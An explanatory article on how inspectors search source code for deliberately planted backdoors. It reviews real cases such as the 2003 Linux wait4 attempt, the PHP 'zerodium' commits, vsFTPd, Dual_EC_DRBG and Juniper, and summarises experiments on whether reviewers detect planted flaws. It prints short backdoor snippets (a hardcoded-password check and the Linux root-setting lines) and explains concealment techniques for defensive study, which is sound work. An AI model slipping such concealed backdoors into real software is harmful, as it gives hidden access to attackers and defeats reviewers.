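# Inspecting Software Source Code for Concealed Backdoors

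## What a concealed backdoor is and what an inspection has to show

In a source code inspection for backdoors, an inspector examines a program's source code on behalf of someone who does not trust its developer, meaning the company, state or project behind it. Governments ask for an inspection before letting a foreign company's equipment into the telephone network, and large customers ask for one when they buy software that will guard their data. A treaty partner may also ask for one if it has to rely on a program that the other side wrote. The inspector wants to know whether the developer has put in a backdoor, which is a hidden function or weakness, placed there on purpose, that lets those who know of it bypass the system's protections. The developer wants a clean report even if the program contains a backdoor.

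### From source code to a running program

Take the login program on a network router. It asks for a name and a password and decides whether to let the person in. A programmer writes it as source code, which a trained reader can follow:

```
if password_is_valid(name, password):
    open_session(name)
else:
    refuse()
```

The router's processor cannot run this text, so a program called a compiler translates it into a binary, a long series of machine instructions that people can read only slowly and with special tools. A real product has thousands of source files and also includes libraries, which are ready-made code that other people wrote. The build is the process, with its tools and settings, that turns all this code into the binary the vendor releases. The vendor sends updates for years after the sale, and each one replaces some or all of that binary. Most commercial vendors release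 only binaries, so a customer who asks to inspect the source is asking for something customers do not normally see.

One extra condition turns the login program into a backdoor:

```
if password == "k7Vw2mQz" or password_is_valid(name, password):
    open_session(name)
```

Thomas and Francillon use almost the same example in *Backdoors*, and they divide every backdoor into four parts: an input source (here the password prompt), a trigger (the secret string and the check for it), a payload (the step that skips the real password check) and a privileged state (an open session that the intruder should not have). A backdoor needs all four to work. To detect one, they say, an analyst has to find both the trigger and the payload and show that the trigger leads to the payload.

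Testing the finished router is a poor way to find the secret string. A tester making a million guesses a second would need almost seven years to try every eight-character string of upper- and lowercase letters and digits, and doubling the length would make the search infeasible. Better test tools narrow the search a good deal. But in the source code, at least in a case as crude as this, anyone who reads the line can see the string.

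### Backdoor or mistake

A vulnerability is a flaw that an attacker can use, whether or not anyone intended it. Suppose the login program copies the user's name into a space with room for eighty characters without checking the length. A longer name overwrites the neighbouring memory, and an attacker who chooses the extra characters carefully can make the program jump to instructions of their choice. Programmers call this a buffer overflow and have introduced such flaws by accident for decades. The router's vulnerability is also a backdoor if the programmer left out the length check deliberately and told a friend, but the source code is the same as if the programmer had forgotten it.

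Thomas and Francillon sort suspicious constructs by what an analyst can establish about them. In an intentional backdoor, such as a secret password, the path from trigger to payload is explicit in the code, and nobody can plausibly call it an accident. In a deniable backdoor, the path runs through what looks like a bug, and only non-technical evidence suggests that it was deliberate. An accidental vulnerability lacks that evidence, and they write that it can't be distinguished from a deniable backdoor on technical grounds alone. *2020 State of the Octoverse* (2021), a security report from the code-hosting company GitHub, uses the term "bugdoor" for a backdoor disguised as a convenient, hard-to-spot error.

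*Backdoor* (Zdziarski, 2016) proposes a different definition, under which a mechanism is a backdoor only if it subverts the purposes disclosed to the computer's owner, is active without the owner's consent, and can be controlled by someone undisclosed. An undocumented maintenance password on a router meets all three tests. An ordinary login check that an attacker has learned to defeat does not, because the owner agreed to run it and the manufacturer built it to do what it was supposed to do. Because it emphasizes disclosure, this definition also covers well-meant hidden logins, which a search for spies might miss. *Static Detection of Application Backdoors* (Wysopal and Eng) notes that manufacturers of network appliances often build in such logins so that support staff can help customers who have lost their own access, but anyone who learns the password can use them. The tests do not resolve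 the problem of the missing length check. Zdziarski acknowledges that a manufacturer could leave a mechanism weak on purpose and that this would be hard to demonstrate.

Most evidence of intent lies outside the code. Thomas and Francillon suggest looking at the version history (the log of who changed which line and when) or comparing successive releases and asking whether a change had any legitimate reason. The program itself can also contain clues, such as a fragment that only raises a user's privileges and is never reached in normal operation. Another clue is a sloppy password routine that runs only when the username is "bugdoor", while every other user gets a sound one. They say that all of this rests on human judgement and none of it amounts to proof. An inspector who receives a single snapshot of the source, without its history, lacks much of this evidence.

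Judging by base rates, a flaw is more likely to be a mistake than a deliberate backdoor. GitHub's analysts examined a random sample of 521 advisories, the public notices that announce flaws in open-source packages, and found that 17% concerned explicitly malicious behaviour. Only 0.2% of the alerts sent to developers whose projects used a flawed package did. These figures are old and cover only open-source packages, so they are weak evidence about a state-backed vendor's router. Any such count also misses some backdoors, because one successfully disguised as a mistake is recorded as a mistake. Still, when an inspector finds a missing length check, the vendor will certainly call it a mistake, and it most likely is one.

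How much it matters whether a flaw was deliberate depends on what the inspection is for. A network operator who only wants to keep intruders out can demand a fix without knowing why the flaw is there. A government that means to ban the vendor, or a treaty partner about to accuse the other side of cheating, needs to show that the flaw was deliberate. A developer who plants a backdoor therefore has a strong reason to make it look like an error, because if an inspector finds it, the developer can apologise and issue a patch.

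### Who might have put it there

The vendor is the most powerful suspect. It writes the source code, owns the machines that build it, chooses the compiler and signs the updates. It also decides what the inspectors see and answers their questions. A handful of engineers who control the build can add a backdoor without the rest of the staff ever learning about it.

A state that compels a vendor can use all those powers and can add legal secrecy. Most products already contain many accidental vulnerabilities that a capable intelligence service could exploit. A US Defense Science Board task force, quoted in a presentation by the code-analysis company Veracode (2007), reasoned that high-end attackers may still prefer to implant their own, because somebody may fix an accidental flaw just before the attacker needs it. A state can also issue its order years after the sale, so an honest vendor with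 a clean product can pass an inspection and receive the order later.

A rogue employee controls far less, because they can change only the code their job gives them access to, and only if colleagues approve the changes. But Schneier (2019), in *Supply-Chain Security and Trust*, estimates that thousands of people could each, acting alone, slip a backdoor into a computer or smartphone. According to Wysopal and Eng, many of those who plant backdoors do it for the challenge, or because they can, with a vague idea that the backdoor might be useful later.

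An outside intruder's reach depends on what they have broken into. *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026) describes three routes into open-source software. An attacker can get a malicious change accepted into the project's shared source code, where it leaves a trace in the version history. An attacker can also tamper with the release package on the download server, which leaves the project's own source clean, or corrupt a library that the project depends on, so that the backdoor enters during the build. Commercial products are exposed to the same three routes, and Wysopal and Eng list a fourth, a compromised compiler or other development tool.

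How far an inspector can rely on a vendor's evidence depends on who is suspected. If the suspect is a rogue employee or an intruder, the vendor is an ally, and its logs, build machines and engineers' explanations are useful. If the suspect is the vendor itself, or a state behind it, the inspector has to confirm the logs and explanations independently or do without them.

### Four claims in one

"This product has no backdoor" sounds like one statement. An inspection can support it only by supporting four, and all of them must hold:

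1. The inspector saw all the relevant code.
2. The inspector would have recognised a backdoor in it.
3. The code that the inspector read is the code that runs on the customer's equipment.
4. It stays so after updates.

Seeing all the code is hard because much of a modern product's code comes from outside the vendor. In GitHub's 2020 data, the median JavaScript project that kept a full list of its dependencies had 683 of them, counting the dependencies of dependencies. Some libraries reach the vendor only as binaries, and Wysopal and Eng warn that a source code review then leaves significant portions of the software unread. Device firmware often comes with neither source code nor development logs, according to *ROSA* (2025), a study of automated backdoor detection. Even if the router's login code is clean, the backdoor may be in the library that implements `password_is_valid`. The relevant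 evidence is an inventory of everything that goes into the build and a test of whether the source the vendor handed over is enough, by itself, to build the product.

An inspector's confidence is weak evidence that they would have recognised a backdoor. Wheeler (2020), in *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code*, points to programming contests whose entrants write malicious code that looks harmless to a human reader. Automated tools miss things too. *Towards a Backdoorless Network Architecture Based on Remote Attestation and Backdoor Inspection* (2020) proposes a design that relies on such tools, but states that none of them can guarantee a backdoor's absence. Better evidence comes from experiments in which someone plants known backdoors and counts how many the reviewers or tools find. These experiments estimate the detection probability, the chance that an inspection finds a backdoor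 that is present, but only for backdoors like the ones planted.

Reading more source code doesn't show whether the running code matches the inspected code. A subverted compiler or a compromised download site adds the backdoor after the programmers hand over the source, and Wysopal and Eng conclude that only analysis of the binary can then find it. To check for a match, the inspector builds a binary from the inspected source and compares it with the one on the customer's router. The comparison is exact if the vendor has set up a reproducible build, which gives the same binary bit for bit every time, but otherwise someone has to explain every difference.

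An inspection report applies only to the version inspected, and a single release can alter millions of lines. If the inspectors need six months and the vendor ships a new version every month, their report describes a program that customers have already replaced several times. Kokkonis and colleagues built a tool called Lily to vet changes to open-source projects. Lily compares each version with the one before, so it cannot detect a backdoor that was there from the start. They therefore recommend a thorough one-time audit of the existing code, for which they think ROSA is better suited, followed by a check of every change. To count as evidence, inspection has to be a continuing arrangement in which the inspector sees each update before customers install it.

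An attacker needs only one of the four claims to be false. An intruder on the download server can give the customer a backdoor even if the source is clean and the inspectors read it without error. A vendor can target whichever claim the inspectors have tested least. Another month of reading source code adds little assurance if nobody has compared the binaries.

### Inspecting against someone who expects it

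Software companies routinely review code, mostly to find errors. Schneier, in *Security Engineering*, uses two imaginary machines to explain how security work differs. Murphy's computer suffers random faults, which engineers know a good deal about handling. Satan's computer contains an intelligent adversary who makes things fail in the worst way at the worst moment. The phrase "Satan's computer" comes from Anderson and Needham's *Programming Satan's Computer*, which is about cryptographic protocols, short exchanges of perhaps two to five messages by which computers identify each other. These protocols are far smaller than a router's software, yet researchers kept finding errors in well-known ones years after publication. Anderson and Needham attributed the difficulty of getting them right to the presence of a hostile opponent.

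Methods that work well against accidental errors can fail badly against a deliberate backdoor. A quality reviewer who reads a randomly chosen tenth of the files gets a fair idea of how many errors the rest contain, because nobody placed those errors to avoid review. The same sample has a one-in-ten chance of including the one file with the backdoor, and no chance if the developer can guess which files the reviewer will pick. A product with two serious bugs is better than one with forty, but a single working backdoor gives its owner all the access they need, and forty accidental bugs help to hide it. The developer can also run commercial scanning tools on the code before the inspectors arrive and rewrite the backdoor until the tools no longer flag it.

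Wysopal and Eng observed that most security reviews look for vulnerabilities rather than backdoors, and that the habits of one search do not fully carry over to the other. A reviewer looking for known kinds of mistakes has a fair chance of catching a bugdoor such as a missing length check, but without learning whether the flaw was deliberate. The same reviewer may overlook a tidy, well-tested function that contains no errors but does not belong in the product.

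## How backdoors are hidden in readable source code

An attentive reader would notice the secret password in the router example, but real backdoors have sat in published code and standards, a few of them for years. Some were crude and lasted only until someone looked. Others resembled a typing error, or made the code on the screen differ from the code the compiler translated. In the hardest to see, the weakness was a number that somebody had chosen, not a programming error.

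### Fixed passwords and hidden commands

For more than seven years, anyone could log in to Borland's Interbase database with the username "politically" and the password "correct". The programmers made no effort to disguise this in the source code, which Wysopal and Eng reproduce and which calls the two values LOCKSMITH_USER and LOCKSMITH_PASSWORD. But customers had only the binaries, and the login was discovered when the source was released to the public. A fixed password in Cart32, a shopping-cart program, opened a list of every shop on the server and went unnoticed for more than five years.

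Crude backdoors in code that outsiders can read have been found sooner. Among the cases Wysopal and Eng collected, somebody spotted a hidden command shell in TCP Wrappers, a network access filter, within 12 hours, and altered files in the blogging program WordPress within a week. A backdoor in OpenSSH, a remote-login program, lasted two days in 2002, even though the intruder had disguised the malicious file as a test of an encryption routine, where a long table of meaningless numbers looks normal. The numbers decoded into a script that took commands from a remote server. The list includes only backdoors that somebody found, so it can't show how many others are still in place.

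The file-transfer server vsFTPd had an undisguised backdoor. In the summer of 2011, an intruder replaced the source package on the project's download site with an altered copy that opened a command shell to anyone whose username contained a smiley face. "There is no obfuscation," wrote the program's author, Chris Evans, quoted in Threatpost's *Vsftpd FTP Server Download Site Compromised*. The altered code escaped notice because few people read such a package before compiling and installing it. *Popular FTP package download tarball poisoned* (Leyden, 2011) reports that the package stayed up for about three days and had an invalid digital signature, so checking the signature would have given users a warning. Evans (2011) found it strange that the intruder had remembered to set a plausible date on the package but had left compiled files inside, which changed its size radically. Evans learned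 of the backdoor from a user's tip and suspected a prank. In the same mailing-list discussion, the security researcher HD Moore pointed to a copy on a mirror site in Namibia and doubted that the exposure had been so short.

The attackers who added a backdoor to PHP, a programming language that runs a large share of the world's websites, falsified the descriptions and authorship of their changes but did not disguise the code. PHP's developers found two malicious changes in the official source repository on 28 March 2021. PHP.Watch's *git.php.net server compromised, move to GitHub, and delayed updates* (2021) reports that both were described as "Fix typo" and carried the names of trusted people, the project's founder Rasmus Lerdorf and the maintainer Nikita Popov. The added code let a visitor run commands on any website using that version of PHP if the text the browser sent to identify itself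 began with "zerodium". Popov told BleepingComputer that the first change was "rather obviously malicious" and was found during a routine review a couple of hours after it was made. The developers removed both changes before any release.

The names on the changes misled even PHP's maintainers for a while. According to Popov's later account, he first suspended Lerdorf's access, which made no sense in hindsight because anyone who can submit a change to the version-control system can put any author's name on it. When the second change appeared under his own name, Popov checked the server logs and eventually found that the attacker had logged in with a username and password, by a route he had not known the server offered. An inspector who relies on the version history as evidence of who did what, and why, therefore needs to know whether the developer authenticated the names in it.

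### A slip of one character

The attempt on Linux in November 2003 needed two lines:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
    retval = -EINVAL;
```

The 2003 attempt to backdoor Linux added two lines to `wait4`, a function in the kernel (the core of the operating system) that a program calls to wait for another program to finish. A programmer skimming the lines would take them for a routine check that returns an error if a program asks for an odd combination of options and its user is number 0, the administrator account called root. But in the C language, `==` compares two values, while a single `=` changes the value on the left. Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) explains that the second condition uses `=`, so it makes the user root instead of checking whether the user is root. C then treats the resulting zero as "false" and skips the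 second line, so no error appears.

Linux developers kept their master copy in a system called BitKeeper, and a converted copy in another system, CVS, served those who preferred it. Somebody broke into the machine that held the CVS copy and changed the files. Larry McVoy, whose company ran the conversion, said in Miller and Barr's *Linux kernel development process thwarts subversion attempt* that a script compared the two sets of files every night and flagged the difference. The change also lacked the usual pointer to a record in the master copy.

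A bookkeeping check caught the change before anyone understood it. In his first message to the kernel developers, *BK2CVS problem*, McVoy (2003) called the incident "not a big deal" and did not quote the two lines. Another developer asked, out of curiosity, what they were. When McVoy posted them, one reader replied "That looks odd" and another "Not if you hope to get root." McVoy then admitted that he had missed the single equals sign, even though he had already looked at the file and repaired it. In *Trojan Source*, Boucher and Anderson credit experienced developers with detecting the attack, but the order of the messages suggests that those developers would not have looked at the lines without the bookkeeping check.

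Linus Torvalds, who leads Linux development, said in the same discussion that this change could not have reached an official release, because nobody who fed code into the master copy worked from the CVS version. He also told Miller and Barr that a similar change to a project's core files could be very hard to detect, since two lines out of five million are easy to miss. Dilger (2003), another kernel developer, thought that without review the change might have taken a long time to find. Theodore Ts'o described a more worrying route, in which someone forges an email from a trusted developer and hides the lines among other plausible changes. In the later "hypocrite commits" study, researchers tested the kernel's reviewers with deliberately flawed patches.

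Writing `=` for `==` is a common mistake, so the code alone would have supported a weak case that the programmer had made an honest error. A reader of Freedom to Tinker's account pointed out that even the corrected check makes no sense, because the combination of options is harmless and there is no reason to forbid it to root alone. The break-in showed that the change was deliberate. There was no such evidence for a flaw discovered in 2006 in X.Org, the software that draws windows on many Linux screens. Its programmers meant to reserve certain dangerous options for root, but in one place they left out a pair of brackets, so the program tested whether a function existed instead of what it returned. The test always succeeded, and ordinary users got the options too. Nobody had broken into a server, and the missing brackets could not show what the programmer intended. Wysopal and Eng judge that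 this was probably an honest error, with "no way to be certain".

### A contest for innocent-looking code

Scott Craver of Binghamton University started the Underhanded C Contest, a public competition in this kind of concealment, in 2005. In each round, the organisers set an ordinary programming task and specified a harmful behaviour to hide. Entrants had to write C code that seemed to do the task but secretly carried out the harmful behaviour. The judges read the source, so it had to look clear and harmless. Short programs earned more credit than long ones because they leave less room to hide anything.

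The judges also rewarded deniability, favoring entries whose flaw, in their opinion, would still look like an innocent mistake after someone found it. Boucher and Anderson list techniques that entrants commonly used, including reading or writing past the end of a block of memory, misusing macros (shorthand that expands into longer code), and swapping `=` and `==`, as in the Linux case.

For the 2015 round, the organisers worked with the Nuclear Threat Initiative, a nuclear security non-profit, and chose a treaty inspection as the setting. The program had to compare an object's radiation spectrum with that of a reference warhead and report only whether they matched. The hidden fault had to make it report a false match. Linus Åkesson won with a program in two files that use the same name for a type of number. Because of the way each file picks up its definitions, the name means an eight-byte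 number in one file and a four-byte number in the other. The comparison routine therefore misreads the measurements and can accept a spectrum it should reject.

Each file looks correct to a reviewer who checks them one at a time. If someone finds the mismatch, the programmer can blame a clash with a name in the standard mathematics library, a mistake that an honest programmer could make. The contest shows that such code is possible in programs short enough to read in one sitting. It doesn't measure how often reviewers would catch a backdoor, since the judges knew that every entry was malicious and were looking for the trick.

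### Text that displays as a different program

Unlike in the earlier examples, the code a reader sees can differ from the code the compiler processes, as Boucher and Anderson showed in 2021. Modern text uses Unicode, a standard that assigns a number to every character in the world's scripts. Some scripts run left to right and others right to left, so Unicode includes invisible control characters that set the display order of a stretch of text. Compilers mostly ignore display order and process characters in the order they are stored in the file.

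Most programming languages reject control characters in the code itself but accept them in comments (notes for human readers, which the compiler skips) and in quoted text. An attacker can put them there to change how the code on the rest of the line is displayed. In one of the paper's examples, a short Python program appears to take 50 from a bank balance of 100. The balance stays at 100 when the program runs, because the word `return`, which looks like part of a comment, is an instruction that ends the function before the subtraction. In another example, a check that the user is an administrator looks like working code but is inside a comment, so the compiler skips it.

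Boucher and Anderson built working demonstrations in 12 languages. They also tested common code editors and three code review websites. Most displayed the deceptive version, though the editor vim showed the control characters as visible codes. The colouring of comments and code sometimes looked wrong, but Boucher and Anderson expected most developers not to notice. A related trick uses letters that look alike. A compiler treats the Latin H and the Cyrillic Н as different characters, so a program can contain two functions that both seem to be called `sayHello`.

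Researchers discovered the method themselves, rather than finding it in a victim's code. The announcement, *Trojan Source* (2021), on the Cambridge security blog Light Blue Touchpaper, describes a 99-day embargo during which many makers of compilers, editors and code repositories added defences. Critics quoted by TechTarget objected that programmers had known for years how to hide code in this way. Criminals have since used invisible characters in real attacks. In the GlassWorm campaign, the first sign researchers noticed was an infected program's abnormal behaviour, according to iTnews' *Hidden "Glassworm" malware spreads through infected VS Code extensions*.

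In its reordering form, this is the easiest concealment for an inspector to rule out. The paper lists the nine relevant control characters, and a simple search of the stored files finds every one. Look-alike letters take more judgement because a program may legitimately contain Cyrillic text, but the Rust compiler already warned about them before the researchers published their findings. Neither check works on a printout, or on a screen where the vendor controls the display software, so the inspector needs access to the files themselves.

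### Correct code built around a chosen number

Encryption depends on random numbers, because anyone who can predict them can work out the secret keys. Computers produce most of theirs with a generator, a procedure that calculates a long series of random-looking numbers from a secret starting value. The US standards agency NIST published one such generator, Dual_EC_DRBG, in 2006. The National Security Agency (NSA), which both makes and breaks codes, had contributed to the standard.

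The generator works with points on an elliptic curve, a set of points for which mathematicians have defined a kind of addition. Adding a point to itself *n* times amounts to multiplying it by *n*. This is quick even for an enormous *n*, but nobody knows a practical way for ordinary computers to go backwards and find *n* from the starting point and the result. The standard prints two fixed points, *P* and *Q*. Each round then goes as follows:

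1. The generator multiplies *P* by its current secret value and takes the horizontal coordinate of the result, a number *r*.
2. It multiplies *Q* by *r*, takes the horizontal coordinate, drops 16 bits and releases the rest as its random output.
3. It multiplies *P* by *r*, and the horizontal coordinate of that point becomes the secret value for the next round.

On the curves in the standard, some number *e* always exists for which *P* = *eQ*. Shumow and Ferguson, in *On the Possibility of a Back Door in the NIST SP800-90*, slides that the two Microsoft researchers presented in August 2007, worked out what follows if an attacker knows *e*. The attacker sees one block of output and tries all 65,536 possibilities for the missing 16 bits, which gives a short list of candidates for the point *rQ*. Multiplying the right candidate by *e* gives

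*e*(*rQ*) = *r*(*eQ*) = *rP*,

and the horizontal coordinate of *rP* is the generator's next secret value. From then on the attacker can calculate every number the generator will produce. Project Bullrun's *Dual EC DRBG* puts the output needed at 32 bytes. On the smallest of the standard's curves, one block supplies 30 of those bytes, and the other two serve to weed out the wrong candidates.

Whoever chose the points could have picked *e* first and calculated one point from the other. Anyone else would have to solve the backward problem to find it. The standard did not state where *Q* came from, and the printed coordinates look equally random whether or not anyone knows *e*. A programmer could therefore implement the standard faithfully, and an inspector could check every line against it, without either learning whether someone holds the secret.

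In November 2007, Schneier on Security's *The Strange Story of Dual_EC_DRBG* brought that year's clear, public warning to a wide audience. It also noted that researchers had found a small bias in the generator's output in early 2006. Project Bullrun cites a later NIST presentation, according to which the issue of the points had first come up in a meeting of X9, a standards committee for the financial industry. The generator remained in use despite this. According to Niederhagen, in *Dual EC*, the security company RSA had made it the default in BSAFE, its toolkit for programmers, in 2004.

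In September 2013, news reports based on documents leaked by Edward Snowden appeared to confirm that the NSA had created the generator with a backdoor. RSA then told developers to stop using its default generator, as Cryptography Engineering's *The Many Flaws of Dual_EC_DRBG* (2013) records, and NIST withdrew its approval the next year. The mathematics, which had been available for six years by then, proved that somebody could hold a key but not that anybody did. The leaked documents supplied evidence for this that reading the code could not have provided.

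In December 2015 Juniper Networks, an American maker of network equipment, announced that an internal code review had found unauthorised code in ScreenOS, the operating system of its NetScreen firewalls. ScreenOS used Dual_EC_DRBG with Juniper's own *Q*, which somebody had replaced in 2012. Juniper had said that a second generator processed the output before it left the device, which would have defeated the attack. Outside researchers analysed the firmware and found that a programming error kept the second generator from ever running. Whoever knew the secret behind the new *Q* could therefore decrypt private traffic that passed through the firewalls without breaking into any system.

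Someone had replaced one long number in Juniper's source code with another, and the program worked as well as before. Juniper took about three years to notice. The review that found the change also found a fixed password that let anyone log in as administrator. Its author had made it look like the templates programmers use for log messages. A search for suspicious text could have found the password, but not the changed number.

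### What the inspector has to read for

Finding a fixed password or a hidden command takes thoroughness more than brilliance. The inspector has to work out why each piece of code is in the product, including the test files and installation scripts, where the OpenSSH intruder hid malicious code. Wysopal and Eng suggest starting with every fixed piece of text that the program compares with something a user types. A team can get through a large product this way, because most code has an obvious purpose and needs only a glance.

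Reading for errors is far slower. The inspector has to work out what each line does, rather than what its author seems to have meant, and check the assumptions that pass between files, as in Åkesson's entry. This is worth the time for code that controls logins and privileges. Wysopal and Eng recommend looking there for conditions that change a value or always give the same answer, which would have caught both the Linux lines and the X.Org brackets. It is sensible to have the vendor fix every error, planted or accidental, and to record where they cluster.

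To check a constant such as *Q*, a cryptographer needs to ask where the number came from. An honest designer can publish a starting value and the procedure that turns it into the constant, so that anyone can repeat the calculation and see that there was little room to choose. The NIST standard described such a procedure for users who wanted their own points, but made it optional. If the vendor can't produce a derivation, the inspector should ask for a new constant that has one, without waiting for proof that somebody holds the secret. Larger design choices need the same scrutiny because a vendor can deliberately weaken them, as did Crypto AG, a Swiss cipher-machine maker secretly part-owned by the CIA. Inspecting the source in this way won't catch a backdoor that enters later, through a doctored release package, as with XZ Utils in 2024, or through the compiler.

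## How well human reviewers find planted flaws

Researchers have run only a few experiments in which reviewers look for planted flaws, mostly with small programs. The results vary with the size of the code, the kind of flaw and what the reviewers know when they start.

### Reading from the inputs inwards

Reviewers of a large program usually begin by mapping where untrusted data enters, rather than reading from the first file to the last. On the router, these entry points are the login prompt, the administration web page, packets from the network and update files. Reviewers also list the privileged actions, such as opening a session or replacing the software. Then they follow each path from an input to a privileged action and check what controls it. In the login program, a reviewer would search for every line that calls `open_session` and work backwards to the condition that allows the call.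 This search would reveal a secret password as an extra condition and a hidden maintenance login as an extra caller.

Reviewers read the code on these paths line by line. If a line looks wrong, the reviewer works out what input would exploit it and tries that input on the running program, often with a debugger, a tool that pauses a program and displays its memory. According to *CRV2 Introduction*, a guide from the software security non-profit OWASP, manual review is valuable mainly because the reviewer understands the context and can judge how much damage a flaw could do in a particular product. Understanding the context also helps a reviewer notice a function that doesn't belong in the product.

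This method does not expose a backdoor like the chosen constant in Dual_EC_DRBG, which opens no suspicious path.

### Flaws planted in small programs

In a graduate security course at Rice University, pairs of students worked on a demonstration voting machine with about 2,000 lines of clean, well-commented Java code. Each pair first played a corrupt developer and had two weeks to hide malicious changes in the code. Each pair then had one week, alongside other work, to find the changes in two other pairs' programs. The students knew the original program, but they could not use a computer to compare it with the altered versions, because that would have shown them which lines had changed.

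Several pairs designed their changes to survive testing. One change stole votes only on machines numbered above two, because the pair assumed testers would set up at most two. Another started stealing only after voters had cast a certain number of ballots. One pair made the voters' PINs predictable by deriving them from the current second of the hour, which left only 3,600 possible starting points.

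Two pairs audited each program. Both pairs found the malicious change in about two-thirds of cases, and at least one pair found it in every case but one, an option that cut a voting terminal off from the console that checks PINs. A single pair therefore had very roughly an 80% chance of finding the change. Some auditors found a change without understanding it. One pair of students had rewritten the test for whether two candidates are the same person, so that it merged two candidates if one's name was the beginning of the other's. One candidate would then get both candidates' votes, and the other would disappear from the results. Auditors noticed the altered code but did not work out its effect. A bug in the code may have confused them. In a real inspection, they might have accepted a harmless explanation from the developer.

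These conditions were easy because the program was tiny, and the auditors knew the original and knew somebody had tampered with it. Science Applications International Corporation independently reviewed the more than 50,000 lines of code in a real Diebold voting machine. One of its employees thought it would be easy to hide malicious code there, with a 99.9% chance that nobody would notice. That was one practitioner's guess about a program of ordinary size.

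Professional developers have also done poorly on small programs. In an experiment published in 2013, researchers hired 30 of them to review a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities, all of common kinds such as SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into an input field. Nobody found all seven. More experienced developers did not necessarily do better, and those who reported more real flaws also tended to report more false ones. A customer hiring inspectors therefore can't rely on their years of experience or the number of flaws they report. A trial review of code with known flaws would be a better test. Nobody had disguised the seven vulnerabilities, so the developers would probably do worse at finding a deliberate backdoor.

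Reviewers are much more likely to find a flaw when they are told to look for one. In an online experiment, researchers gave 146 participants code that failed to check its input safely. Many who missed the flaw at first found it once the researchers warned them that it was there, but 60 still could not. In a later experiment with 150 participants, asking reviewers to concentrate on security made them eight times as likely to find the vulnerability. Adding a security checklist brought no significant further improvement, even when the researchers tailored it to the code.

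An inspector has part of this advantage because they look for security problems from the start, which the vendor's own staff often don't do. PortSwigger's *The road to DevSecOps isn’t always the smoothest* describes a study, based on interviews with 10 developers and a survey of 182 others, which concluded that security was "not a priority during review". In the cases that researchers examined from Chromium, the open-source project behind Google's browser, about 1% of reviewers' comments dealt with security. Reviewers there tended to miss buffer overflows and other language-specific problems. A vendor's assurance that colleagues review every change is therefore weak evidence that the reviewers would have stopped a bugdoor.

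### Flawed patches sent to Linux

In *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software*, Wu and Lu of the University of Minnesota tested whether an outsider could slip a vulnerability into the Linux kernel through a "hypocrite commit", a small patch that fixes a real but minor problem and creates a serious one. The reviewers did not know that they were in an experiment.

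Wu and Lu chose a type of vulnerability called use-after-free, in which a program releases a block of memory and later uses it again by mistake. By then, an attacker may have filled the block with their own data. The kernel has thousands of places where either the release or the later use is already present and a small change could add the other. The two researchers wrote software to find such places.

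In one of their patches, the existing code requests two blocks of memory and doesn't free the first if the second request fails. The patch frees it, which looks correct to a reviewer who reads only the patch. But another part of the kernel goes on using the same block through a different pointer. To find the vulnerability, the reviewer has to know what the calling function does after the second request fails, which testing rarely covers.

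The paper describes three such patches, each with fewer than five changed lines, which the researchers emailed to maintainers under false names in August 2020. When the experiment became widely known, kernel developers objected that they had not agreed to take part and that the researchers had wasted their time and abused their trust. Wu and Lu acknowledged that most maintainers are volunteers. The researchers defended the experiment in the University of Minnesota's *Clarifications on the “hypocrite commit” work (FAQ)*, saying that the flawed patches never left the email exchanges and that no Linux user was at risk. They also wrote in the paper that the patches would eventually help to fix three real bugs.

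In April 2021 a senior kernel developer, Greg Kroah-Hartman, suspected that the group had resumed sending bad code. According to Desde Linux's *Audit completed for all patches submitted by the University of Minnesota*, he asked the community to refuse patches from the university and re-examine those it had already accepted. The researchers withdrew their paper. The university's computer science department apologised for an "inappropriately designed" project in its *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021).

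The re-examination by the Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board and other developers reflected better on the reviewers than the paper had. The board traced five patches to the study. Four contained vulnerabilities, and Desde Linux reports that maintainers rejected all four. TechRadar's *Linux review board says rogue researchers did not successfully insert buggy patches* also reports that none of the deliberately flawed code reached the main kernel. Four patches are too few to support a detection rate, and a maintainer can reject a patch for another reason without noticing the vulnerability.

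The same exercise also uncovered flaws that reviewers had missed. According to Tom's Hardware's *Linux Foundation Issues Frosty Final Judgment in UMN Scandal*, the board reviewed 435 earlier changes from the university, which maintainers had accepted as honest contributions. Most were correct, but 39 were faulty and still needed repair. As far as anyone could tell, these were ordinary mistakes. The board recommended that the university review its patches internally before sending more, according to *The TAB report on the UMN affair*.

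Wu and Lu's historical figures are more informative than their patches. They collected use-after-free vulnerabilities from January 2015 to August 2020 and calculated the share that maintainers had caught in review. Maintainers caught 56.6% of those that a person or a simple tool could reasonably find. The rate was 42.0% for flaws in error-handling code, 38.4% for flaws involving two names for the same memory, and 19.4% for flaws that depended on the timing of two tasks running at once.

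Wu and Lu call these rates upper limits because nobody can count the missed flaws that are still undiscovered. Counting patches that maintainers turned down without naming the flaw would raise the rates. The flaws were also accidental, whereas an attacker can choose the kind that reviewers find hardest to catch and, as Wu and Lu point out, submit another patch after a rejection. One honest patch that resembled Wu and Lu's left a vulnerability in the kernel for five years.

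An inspection team can measure its own detection rate without deceiving volunteers. If the managers and the developer agree, a colleague can plant flaws in a private copy of the code and leave the reviewers to find them without saying which files contain them.

### What reviews of real products could say

In 2007, California commissioned university researchers to examine three vendors' voting systems, in one of the most thorough public code reviews. *Source Code Review of the Sequoia Voting System* (Blaze, Cordero and colleagues, 2007) describes how eight reviewers worked for six weeks in a locked, alarmed room on more than 800,000 lines of code. They asked which components the system trusted, how it protected votes and keys, and whether anyone would notice tampering, and then read only the most critical sections closely. If they found several related flaws in one part, they moved on to another,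 because more flaws in the same part would add little to what an attacker could already do.

The team found serious weaknesses throughout. Sequoia had hardcoded its secret encryption keys and apparently used the same ones in every jurisdiction, so anyone who obtained similar hardware outside California could extract the keys that protected the state's elections. None of the software update mechanisms could reliably detect or prevent tampering. California Secretary of State Debra Bowen withdrew approval of the reviewed systems, then reapproved them under stricter conditions.

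The team gave almost no assurance that it would find backdoors, describing its method as "particularly unlikely to discover deliberately introduced and obfuscated flaws". It judged that even a very thorough manual review would be doing very well by industry standards if it found half of all problems. The team also lacked the full set of build tools, so it could not check that the source code matched the software on the machines.

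In *California voting systems code review now released*, Blaze (2007) thought a well-disguised backdoor would be almost impossible to detect. He also thought one would be "largely superfluous" in the California voting systems, because their ordinary flaws already offered so many ways in. Those flaws were reason enough for election officials to act, but the review could not have shown whether a vendor had planted a backdoor.

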